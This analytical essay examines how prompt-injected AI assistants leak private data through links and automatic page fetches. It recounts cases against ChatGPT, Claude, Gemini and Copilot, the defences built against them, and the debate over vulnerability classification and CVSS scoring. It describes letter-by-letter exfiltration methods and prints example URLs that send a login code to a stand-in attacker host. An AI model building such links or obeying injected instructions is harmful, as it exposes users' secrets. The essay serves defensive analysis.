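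Lists of allowed sites for AI agents have failed in similar ways, as Willison describes in two cases that PromptArmor found. The browser tool in Antigravity, Google's programming environment, could by default visit only listed sites, but the list included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and read the requests sent to it. Anthropic's Claude Cowork was allowed to contact Anthropic's own servers. The attacker's instructions included a key to the attacker's Anthropic account, and the agent uploaded the user's files to that account.

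Both lists answered the question of whether a site was reputable. The sites were, but an attacker could still receive data through them.

### OpenAI's check of the exact address

In January 2026, OpenAI described a different check, which tests whether the exact address has already appeared in public. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that browses the public web and indexes the addresses it finds, much as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. Before ChatGPT fetches an address automatically, the system looks for it in the crawler's index. If the address is there, ChatGPT may load it. Otherwise, the system either directs the model to try another website or shows the user a warning.

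Take the two addresses from the login-code example:

```
https://attacker.example/view
https://attacker.example/view?c=482913
```

The crawler may well have found the first URL, if the attacker put a link to it on a public page. It is very unlikely to have found the second, because the attacker would have had to publish the code before stealing it. ChatGPT can therefore load the first automatically but not the second, even though both are on the same site.

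This is why the site's reputation doesn't matter much. An address on the attacker's own site can pass if it existed before the conversation, because the user's data can't have been written into it. The Google Form used against Superhuman was on a trusted domain, but an address that filled in the form with a particular user's emails would have failed because it would not have been in any index. An address on a trusted site would also fail if its query string contained an attacker's address with a secret attached.

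This works only if the index is independent. If OpenAI added every address its users' assistants visited, an address containing one user's secret could become "public" just because ChatGPT had once opened it.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) calls the mechanism Safe Url. It also covers pages that the agent opens and bookmarks in Atlas, OpenAI's web browser, and searches and page visits in Deep Research, the feature that ShadowLeak exploited. Similarly, Canvas and ChatGPT Apps, which let ChatGPT create and use small programs, run those programs in a sandbox that detects unexpected communication and asks for the user's consent. OpenAI adds that most of the attacks it knows of fail earlier, because the model refuses to carry them out.

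The check inconveniences users when a legitimate address is not in the index. A news article published ten minutes ago may not have been indexed yet, and a private document on a company's server never should be. Many ordinary links also contain tracking codes unique to one recipient. The check cannot distinguish any of these from an address containing stolen data.

In its technical paper on the check, OpenAI acknowledges a way around it that Rehberger had described in 2023. He explains in the analysis on Embrace The Red that an attacker can have the model spell out a secret one character at a time, as in CamoLeak, using a public page for each letter and digit. That takes 36 pages, and anyone with a fairly large blog probably already has that many in the index.

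Rehberger raises two other problems. As he understands it, ChatGPT treats a URL as safe for the rest of the chat if the user has entered it in a message. That is sensible when the user types the URL, but a user who pastes in a stranger's email may also be entering the stranger's URLs. The second problem is that every team at OpenAI has to remember to use the check. The 2023 version was at first missing from ChatGPT's iOS and macOS apps.

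The check also doesn't protect against phishing. A fake login page with a fixed address can be in the index, and OpenAI says the check doesn't make a page's content trustworthy.

### Claude's limits on which pages it opens

Anthropic tries to do much the same thing without an index of the public web. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the tool Claude uses to open pages accepts only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, such as those in the user's messages or search results. Ordinary software enforces this rule by comparing strings, so no wording in the attacker's email can override it.

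The rule is only as safe as the sources it accepts addresses from. Willison pointed out in September 2025 that many developers paste untrusted text into what the software treats as the user's message, so the rule accepts any address in that text. It also accepts addresses in results from tools that the developer runs, though Anthropic now offers a setting that excludes addresses found only in those results.

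Until July 2026, the tool also accepted addresses found on pages it had already opened, so Claude could follow links from one page to the next. Willison (2026) explains how Ayush Paul exploited this. Paul built a website where each page had a link for every letter, and the site gave Claude a reason to follow the links that spelled the user's name. Claude used only links that the pages offered, and the site's log recorded the name as Claude spelled it. The site showed these pages only to Claude, so a person who visited it to investigate would have seen something else.

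Radware had used the same idea against ChatGPT the previous autumn. After ShadowLeak, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from changing the addresses it was given. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an email that supplied a ready-made address for every character, so ChatGPT did not need to change any. Radware reported a 100% success rate for an improved version of the attack, but not the number of attempts. It reported the flaw in September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in December.

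Anthropic's fix was to stop the fetch tool from following links on the pages it opens. That closed Paul's route, but Claude now can't click through the pages of a manual unless the user or a search provides each address. *The Read-Only Lie*, by the blogger dyb, suggests letting Claude follow links only on websites that the user has named in the conversation. The user would have one more thing to confirm, and an attack from a site like Paul's would work only if the user had deliberately sent Claude there.

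These limits apply only to pages that Claude opens by itself, not to links that a user clicks in an answer.

### How much a choice of address can reveal

Rehberger, Radware and Paul all encoded information in the choice among fixed addresses. This leaks much less than an address the model can write freely, and we can calculate the difference.

Base64 uses 64 (2⁶) different characters, so each one carries at most six bits, and a string of *n* characters carries at most 6*n* bits (Metere, 2026, *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*). A query string with 100 free characters can therefore carry 600 bits, enough for 75 characters of plain English text at the usual eight bits each.

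If the model can only choose among *N* fixed pages, one request carries at most log₂ *N* bits, as with the images in CamoLeak:

| What the attacker's server receives | Most it can reveal | Roughly enough for |
|---|---|---|
| A request for one particular page, or no request | 1 bit | The answer to a yes-or-no question |
| A request for one of 36 pages | 5.2 bits | One letter or digit |
| A request for one of 1,024 pages | 10 bits | Three digits |
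| 30 requests, each for one of 27 pages | 143 bits | A name, an employer and a city |
| One request with 100 free Base64 characters | 600 bits | A sentence |

The fourth row is dyb's estimate for Paul's attack, in which each page offered 26 letters and a hyphen.

A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or about 20 bits. One click on one of 1,024 pages reveals 10 of those bits, which leaves the attacker about 977 codes to choose from. If the login page allowed five guesses, the attacker would get in about once in 200 attacks, compared with once in 200,000 without the leak.

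To get the whole code from one click, the attacker would need a million public pages, one for each possible code, all already recorded by OpenAI's crawler. Each additional bit doubles the number of pages needed. Matching the 600 bits of the free query string would take 2⁶⁰⁰ pages, far more than the number of atoms in the observable universe. Restricting links to fixed public addresses therefore makes a single click nearly useless for stealing a contract or a customer list.

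Some secrets, however, are very short. Whether a company is about to be sold takes one bit to convey, and which of 16 illnesses a patient has takes four. An attacker who knows what to ask could learn either from one click on a link to an ordinary public page. Metere notes more generally that an agent can always reveal one bit by sending or withholding a message, so a defender can realistically only limit how much leaks.

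### Why repetition matters more than a single click

The other way to get more data out is to make more requests. If one request carries log₂ *N* bits, *k* requests carry *k* times as much. With a thousand pages, two requests are enough for a six-digit login code, because each request gives three digits. With ten pages, it takes six requests.

When each request needs a click, the attacker has to persuade the user every time. If clicks are independent and each has the 10% chance assumed earlier, a leak that needs two clicks would succeed once in a hundred attempts, and one that needs six would succeed once in a million. An assistant that opens pages by itself can make the requests without any clicks. By dyb's estimate, Claude made about 30 requests in Paul's attack, all in response to one message from the user.

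Restricting addresses therefore works much better on links that people click than on pages that an assistant opens automatically. Automatic requests also need a control that limits repetition.

One option is to cap the number of requests. Anthropic lets developers set a cap, but there is no default. The cap has to be quite low to protect a short secret. Anthropic's sample code allows five requests. On a site like Paul's, each would carry 4.75 bits, for a total of almost 24. That is more than enough for a login code, though Paul would have needed more to get a name, an employer and a city. Failed requests count toward the limit, which helps a little, but the limit covers only a single turn of the conversation, so an injection that stays in the context could continue in the next turn.

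The fetch tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters. This limit is useful only in addition to a rule against new addresses. If Claude could write addresses freely, it could still fit 225 characters, or 1,350 bits, after `https://attacker.example/`.

Another possible control is caching, which keeps a copy of each page the assistant opens and reuses it the next time, so the website doesn't receive a second request. Rehberger suggested caching, or forbidding an assistant to open the same address twice in a session, as an obstacle to the letter-by-letter method. With one page for each digit, a code with no repeated digits, such as 482913, would still get out, but 482482 would reach the attacker as 482. Only about 15% of six-digit codes (151,200 of a million) have no repeated digits.

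An attacker can get around caching by preparing a separate page for every digit in every position. A six-digit code then takes 60 pages instead of ten. Radware used numbered addresses of this kind because they also preserve the order of characters when requests arrive out of sequence. In Paul's attack, each address was one letter longer than the last, so Claude never had to fetch the same page twice and a cache would have made no difference.

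OpenAI's index would have been a bigger problem for Paul. On a site with 27 links per page, there are about 206 trillion possible ten-character names, each with its own address, and the crawler would have had to record them all in advance. An attacker facing that check would have to go back to a fixed set of numbered pages, which is feasible because ten characters require only 270 pages. The two controls are stronger together than either alone, but data can still leak slowly.

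Metere proposes limiting the leak directly, with software between the agent and the network that keeps a budget of bits for each destination. The software estimates how many hidden bits each message could carry and subtracts them from the budget. The budget refills at a fixed rate, and when it runs out, the software delays or cancels further suspicious messages. The same accounting could apply to addresses by subtracting log₂ *N* bits for each choice among *N* links. An attacker could spread the requests over many domains, so the whole conversation would probably need a budget too.

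A defender could also, in principle, detect the pattern. dyb suggests watching for a rapid series of requests to one site in which each address is one character longer than the last. That would catch Paul's version, but an attacker who knew about the detector would use a different pattern.

### Leaks through ordinary browsing

An attacker may not need to tell the assistant to spell anything. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) studied what a website can learn from the links an AI agent follows during normal work. Suppose a user asks a research agent why influenza can be more dangerous than COVID-19 for children. On a medical page, the attacker has added a link to "supplementary references", which leads to a site offering two topics, clinical outcomes and biological mechanisms. The agent picks the one it needs, and the next page divides that topic further.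 After a few choices, the attacker has a good idea of what the user asked.

In a test with four links to choose from, the agents produced a usable signal in 98.7% of trials, and the researchers identified the right topic in 93.8% of those, with one request each time. Signals that relied on the number or order of requests were less reliable, at 73.5% and 67.9%, partly because of caching and because agents open pages in parallel.

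The full attack, called SNOOP, chooses its next set of links based on what it has learned so far. The researchers tested it on four agents, including OpenAI's Codex, with three different language models. On 500 questions from the StackExchange websites, it recovered the concepts in the user's question with an average F1 score of 0.89. (F1 combines how much of the right answer an attack finds with how much of what it finds is right, and 1 is a perfect score.) SNOOP needed about 6.5 rounds of links per question. In a second test, on conversations with 26 personas, it combined what it learned over many turns into profiles of the users' attributes, interests and preferences, with an F1 score of 0.80.

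Four existing defences against prompt injection changed the scores by less than 0.03. This is unsurprising because they look for malicious instructions or outgoing private data, and the requests here contain no private data. A method that the researchers designed themselves reduced both scores to 0.39. The agent downloads a fixed number of pages, chosen without regard to the user's private information, and then makes its real choice among the downloaded copies. The attacker therefore sees the same kind of requests whatever the user wants to know. The drawback is that the agent downloads pages it doesn't need.

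The researchers did not test SNOOP against a check like OpenAI's. It would presumably stop the attacker from inventing new pages during the conversation, but public pages prepared in advance on likely topics could still pass.

### Browsing only stored copies

The most thorough control on automatic requests is to make none. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) explains that in Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT can browse only pages that OpenAI has already stored, so that "no live network requests leave OpenAI's controlled network". An ordinary cache still sends a request to the attacker's server the first time ChatGPT visits a page. In Lockdown Mode, even the first visit uses a stored copy, so the attacker can't learn anything from which page ChatGPT chooses.

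The protection substantially limits what ChatGPT can do. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* warns that search results may be out of date or missing. Deep Research and agent mode stop working, ChatGPT may not display images in its answers, and it can't download files to analyse. OpenAI designed the mode for people who handle sensitive information and says most users don't need it. Users can turn it off for a single chat.

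Lockdown Mode leaves some routes open. In company-managed workspaces, it doesn't automatically disable connected apps, so an administrator has to decide which of them could pass data to an outsider. It doesn't affect network access in Codex. The restrictions that OpenAI lists also don't include links in ChatGPT's answers. When a user clicks one, their own browser makes the request, outside the network that Lockdown Mode controls, and the user would have to rely on the address check and its warning.

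### What a user can judge from a warning

OpenAI's warning, titled "Check this link is safe", tells the user that the link isn't verified and may share data from the conversation with another website. It also shows the address and lets the user copy or open the link.

This is better than a general reminder to be careful, because it names the actual danger and shows the address that the label was hiding. With the original link from the login-code example, an attentive user would see `c=482913` and might recognise the code. But the model can encode the code in Base64 first, and then the user sees this:

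`https://attacker.example/view?c=NDgyOTEz`

Hardly anyone could tell that this contains a login code. The user can still judge whether the site is familiar and matches the label, but that means relying on the site's reputation, which OpenAI's check was meant to avoid.

A warning could make the decision easier by showing the data instead of the address. According to OpenAI's March 2026 article, ChatGPT sometimes shows the user "the information that would be transmitted" before asking for confirmation. A warning such as "This link will send your login code to attacker.example" would be hard to misunderstand. But the system has to recognise the data to write one, and an attacker can try to disguise it. Reprompt got data past Copilot's safeguards, and ShadowLeak got data past ChatGPT's, in ways that relied on the software not recognising it.

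Neither of OpenAI's articles reports how often people continue after seeing the warning. Data on browsers' full-page warnings about malicious sites may not apply, because those warnings appear for sites already on a blocklist. OpenAI's warning appears when its crawler has not seen an address, and most such addresses are probably harmless. After opening a dozen new articles and private documents through the same dialog, a user has learned to expect no harm. OpenAI makes the same argument against strict lists of trusted sites, saying that frequent false alarms can "train people to click through prompts without thinking".

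People who see the warning have also already decided to click. In an attack like the one on Slack AI, they believe they need the link to get their answer, and the attacker could tell them in the text to expect a routine security check.

Suppose, fairly optimistically, that half of the users who click a link then turn back. The click rate falls from 10% to 5%, and the chance that a user who receives seven such links opens at least one falls from 52% to about 30%. A user who continues still sends the whole query string, which can carry up to 600 bits per 100 characters.

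Refusing to open the unverified address would limit what the same click can leak to the choice of a public page, which is about 10 bits if the attacker has a thousand such pages. A company could reasonably warn users in most conversations and refuse to open the address in those where the assistant has read both private data and something written by a stranger. Users would lose some legitimate links in those conversations, but they could still ask the assistant for a source with a public address.

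## Is a one-click leak a security vulnerability?

A company's effort to control links depends partly on how it classifies the leak. If it accepts a report as a security vulnerability, it normally tracks the repair, may pay the finder and may publish a numbered entry in the public CVE catalogue. If it files the report as something else, the report can wait indefinitely. Amazon and Slack changed their assistants after researchers showed that links in the answers could leak private data, but Google declined to change its assistant.

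### What Google and Microsoft replied

Checkmarx reported the one-click leak in Gemini to Google on 5 October 2025. Google closed the report four days later as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)", but gave a different reason in its written reply. Its security team had decided that the issue was "not severe enough for us to track it as a security bug", because the risk did not justify the monitoring and escalation that tracking involves. Google added that its reward programme covers only flaws that "substantially affect the confidentiality or integrity of user data".

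"Infeasible" suggests that Google can't fix the leak with reasonable effort, while "not severe enough" suggests that even an easy fix wouldn't be urgent. Google didn't explain why stealing a password or a login code would fail its confidentiality test, but presumably the reason is that the user has to click. Checkmarx called the answer acceptable but said that users should then get a warning, because the answer leaves them to manage the risk.

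In a different report, Checkmarx showed Microsoft an image in Copilot Chat that leaked a developer's API key, with no link to click. Microsoft replied on 4 November 2025 that the behaviour did not meet its classification for a security vulnerability. It said the attack needed "multiple non-default user actions", did not reproduce reliably across environments, and triggered warnings designed to reduce the risk. It also cited "Workplace Trust" (probably a slip for Workspace Trust, a feature of Microsoft's code editor), the assumption that users review and trust the code they choose to run. Checkmarx maintains that the leak needs no further action once the assistant has read the attacker's page, though it concedes that getting it to do so can be complicated.

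Microsoft's severity classification for AI systems (Microsoft, 2023) is better evidence of its position on one-click leaks than its reply, which was not a decision about them. Microsoft rates a prompt injection that steals another user's data as "Critical" if it needs no user interaction and "Important" if it needs "one or more clicks". By this standard, a click lowers the severity by one level, but the leak is still a vulnerability. The classification is only a guideline, and Microsoft also considers how easy an attack is to carry out.

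Microsoft's point about reproducibility is harder to apply to AI than to ordinary software. *Measuring the Vulnerability Disclosure Policies of AI Vendors* (2025) notes that AI vulnerabilities often exploit probabilistic systems, which complicates classifying, reporting and fixing them. An injection that works one time in ten may be hard for an engineer to investigate, but an attacker can still exploit it by sending more emails.

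### The vendors' case

Neither company set out a full argument, but the case for not treating a one-click leak as a vulnerability would go roughly like this:

1. Nothing leaks unless a person decides to click.
2. Emails, search results and ordinary websites also contain harmful links, and nobody considers a mail program vulnerable because it displays one.
3. A complete fix would remove links that users need.
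4. Harmful links in an assistant's answers are therefore a general risk of using the web, and not a flaw in the assistant.

Companies routinely accept flaws that need a click as vulnerabilities, so the click alone doesn't rule out a one-click leak. Microsoft gave SearchLeak a CVE number and fixed it, although the victim had to follow a link to start the attack.

The comparison with other harmful links works for phishing. The links that Permiso placed in ChatGPT's answers had fixed addresses, so anyone could have emailed the same links. But a stranger can't email someone a link containing that person's login code, because the stranger doesn't know the code. Something with access to the mailbox has to write that link, and in a one-click leak the assistant writes it.

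The difficulty of a complete fix is a serious objection, but a partial fix is feasible, because OpenAI already checks whether an exact address was public before the conversation. Google has an enormous search index of public addresses, so its claim that a fix is "infeasible" needs more explanation than it gave Checkmarx. The difficulty of a fix is a reason to leave a flaw in place, but it doesn't affect whether the flaw exists.

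Google has another category, "abuse risks", that suits the vendors' argument better. Its *Abuse Vulnerability Reward Program Rules* distinguish these risks, which are often inherent in useful features, from vulnerabilities, which require a fix. Google says that such features often shouldn't be disabled but do need protections against exploitation at scale. Links in Gemini's answers could reasonably count as an abuse risk, but Google would still have to consider whether removing links to known malicious sites is enough protection.

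### The case against the vendors

The opposing argument is about what the assistant has done before the user clicks:

1. The link appears in a product that the user trusts, as part of an answer the user asked for.
2. The assistant built the address from private data, on a stranger's instructions.
3. The user can't see what following the link will disclose.
4. People who don't know what a click will disclose have not agreed to disclose it.
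5. The product therefore helps an outsider obtain private data without the user's permission, which makes the leak a vulnerability.

The strongest part of this case is the way the assistant builds the address, because it distinguishes the leak from ordinary phishing and doesn't depend on the user's state of mind. A vendor could answer that the flaw is the prompt injection, which nobody knows how to prevent completely, and that the link is only one way for the data to leave. But images are also only one way for data to leave after a prompt injection, and Microsoft still gave EchoLeak, which used them, a CVE number and blocked the route it used.

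Nobody has measured how much users trust such links, but Google's reward programme for AI flaws offers some indirect evidence that they may. SecurityWeek reported that the programme covers phishing through HTML that an attacker injects into Google-branded sites, if the injection persists, affects other users and appears without a "user-generated content" warning, and if Google finds the attack convincing. The rule wouldn't necessarily cover a link in one Gemini answer, but it reflects the concern that people may mistake an attacker's text for Google's.

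Users can sometimes see what a link will disclose. In the Slack AI attack, the link's address showed the API key to anyone who checked it. But attackers can disguise the data, so a careful user can often miss it. That is enough for the argument, which doesn't require that users can never see the data.

The dispute over consent also affects how to read the rules of Google's AI reward programme, which, according to SecurityWeek, covers attacks that leak sensitive information "without user approval". A one-click leak falls outside that description if the click counts as approval. But someone who clicks "View the full newsletter" has approved opening a newsletter, and it would be odd to say they also approved sending a login code to its publisher.

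People who click a link without reading its URL accept that the website will learn about their visit, for example by receiving their network address or a tracking code. A vendor might argue that this acceptance also covers a one-click leak, but few people would expect the website to receive part of their inbox. The case for consent is much stronger when a user continues after a warning that names the login code and its destination.

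Vendors should bear most of the responsibility for preventing these leaks because they can do so more easily than users. A vendor can inspect the full address and what the assistant has read, and can apply the same check to every answer. Users have to judge each link without seeing the hidden instructions that produced it, although employers can help by training staff. Checkmarx says that vendors nonetheless generally treat this kind of behaviour as a risk the user accepts.

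A link that contains private data because of an injection is better classed as a vulnerability. The vendors have a stronger argument about how urgently they need to fix it.

### How severity scores count the click

The Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) gives a flaw a severity score from 0 to 10. FIRST's *CVSS v3.1 Specification Document* describes the base score as a measure of the flaw's intrinsic characteristics that assumes the reasonable worst case. One part of the score is for impact and another for exploitability:

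`Exploitability = 8.22 × attack vector × complexity × privileges × user interaction`

User interaction has only two values in this version, 0.85 for "none" and 0.62 for "required". The public vulnerability database GCVE (2025) lists the values that Microsoft published for EchoLeak. An attacker could exploit it over a network, with low complexity, no privileges and no user interaction. These values give an exploitability of 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.85, or 3.89.

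The impact part is 4.72. Microsoft judged that the damage could extend beyond the vulnerable component, so the formula multiplies the sum of impact and exploitability by 1.08, which gives 9.3 after rounding up to the next tenth. Changing only user interaction to "required" lowers exploitability to 2.84 and the score to 8.2. EchoLeak would then drop from "critical" to "high" on the scale used by the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD).

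The same change accounts for SearchLeak's two reported scores:

| Flaw | Who chose the values | User interaction | Score | Score with the other interaction value |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Microsoft | None | 9.3 | 8.2 |
| EchoLeak | NVD | None | 7.5 | 6.5 |
| SearchLeak | Microsoft | Required | 6.5 | 7.5 |
| SearchLeak | NVD | None | 7.5 | 6.5 |

NVD chose identical values for the two attacks, so its scores don't distinguish the zero-click attack from the one that needed a click. Microsoft's scores differ by 2.8 points, but the click accounts for only about one point. The rest comes from Microsoft's judgements that EchoLeak could affect other components and let an attacker alter some data.

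Antipov reported that the score of ReLeak's code-interpreter flaw rose from 7.4 to 8.6, and a click may also explain this change. Under the formula, a flaw that exposes confidential data beyond the vulnerable component and does no other damage scores 7.4 if it requires user interaction and 8.6 if it doesn't.

FIRST (2023) stresses that CVSS scores measure severity, not risk. Requiring a click reduces the exploitability part of the score by 27%, regardless of how many people would click. At the 10% click rate assumed earlier, it would reduce successful attacks by 90%. The small difference between 9.3 and 8.2 is therefore not evidence that a one-click leak is almost as dangerous as a zero-click one.

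### Did the US database give SearchLeak 7.5?

Press accounts disagree about the severity score NVD gave a one-click flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw* (2026) reported scores of 6.5 from Microsoft and 7.5 from NVD. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026) gave the same scores and said that NVD had assumed no user interaction. The Next Web called the 7.5 a mistake and wrote that NVD's entry showed the same values as Microsoft's.

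The official records support the higher figure. For SearchLeak, NVD's *CVSS v3.1 Statistics for Microsoft Corporation as of 06/09/2026* (2026) lists Microsoft's value for user interaction as "Required" and NVD's as "None", with the reason "User Interaction not identified". A copy of the NVD entry's change history in *CVE-2026-42824* (2026) dates Microsoft's values to 4 June and NVD's to 8 June. The Next Web may have seen only Microsoft's score, which appears in the entry alongside NVD's.

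NVD's choice doesn't mean that its analysts had found that SearchLeak worked without a click. Varonis didn't publish its explanation until 15 June. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) describes the flaw in one sentence that doesn't mention a click, although the accompanying values list user interaction as required. Microsoft had marked 15 of its 40 entries in NVD's comparison as requiring interaction, and the analysts changed eight of these to "None" for the same stated reason.

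NVD's analysts can also correct a score in the other direction when they find evidence of a click. NVD's *CVSS v3.1 Statistics for Wordfence as of 07/29/2025* (2025) includes one flaw whose user interaction rating they changed from "None" to "Required" because they identified web browsing, link clicking or interaction with a file. Microsoft's 6.5 is therefore the better score for SearchLeak, given what Varonis later disclosed.

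Microsoft nevertheless rated SearchLeak "Critical" on its own scale, whose guideline would suggest "Important" for data theft that needs a click. A company can evidently consider a one-click attack very serious when the stolen data might include anything in an employee's mailbox.

CVSS 4.0 divides required interaction into "passive" and "active", but it's unclear which applies to a one-click leak. Tenable's *CVSSv4 is coming* describes passive interactions as typically involuntary and active ones as intentional. Clicking a link is intentional, which suggests "active". Debricked's *The CVSS score gets updated to CVSS v4.0* instead bases the distinction on whether an educated user could recognise the interaction as part of an attack. If the link has an innocent label and encoded data, "passive" seems more accurate. The proposed *Artificial Intelligence Vulnerability Scoring System* avoids this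 problem by keeping the older options, "none" and "required", and their weights.

### What evidence could settle the disagreement

Much of the disagreement about urgency is about how likely people are to click. The 10% estimate comes from simulated phishing emails, and a company could replace it with its own measurement by inserting harmless test links into its assistant's answers. The test should compare click rates for links beside a complete answer with those for links that users seem to need to get the answer, and rates on phones with rates on computers. At a click rate of 1%, an attacker would need about a hundred displayed links for each success on average, and at 30% only three or four. A very low rate would support Google's view that the problem doesn't deserve escalation.

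To find out whether a click amounts to informed consent, researchers would have to ask people what they thought they were sending. They could show one group an ordinary link, a second group a warning with the full address, and a third group a warning that names the private data in plain words. If most people in the first two groups clicked but couldn't say what the link contained, it would be hard to argue that they had accepted the risk. If people in the third group understood the warning and continued anyway, the vendors' position would be much stronger for products with such a warning.

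The easiest of these questions for vendors to answer is how many useful links a fix would block. Google could compare the links in Gemini's answers with its search index without blocking anything, then count how many would fail the check and how many of those people use. OpenAI could publish similar figures from the check it already runs. If only 1% of the links that people follow failed, Google would have difficulty defending its description of the fix as "infeasible". If 30% failed, and most led to new articles or private documents, Google would have good reason not to block them in every conversation. It could still apply the check only when Gemini has read both private data and text from a stranger, so the failure rate in those conversations matters most.
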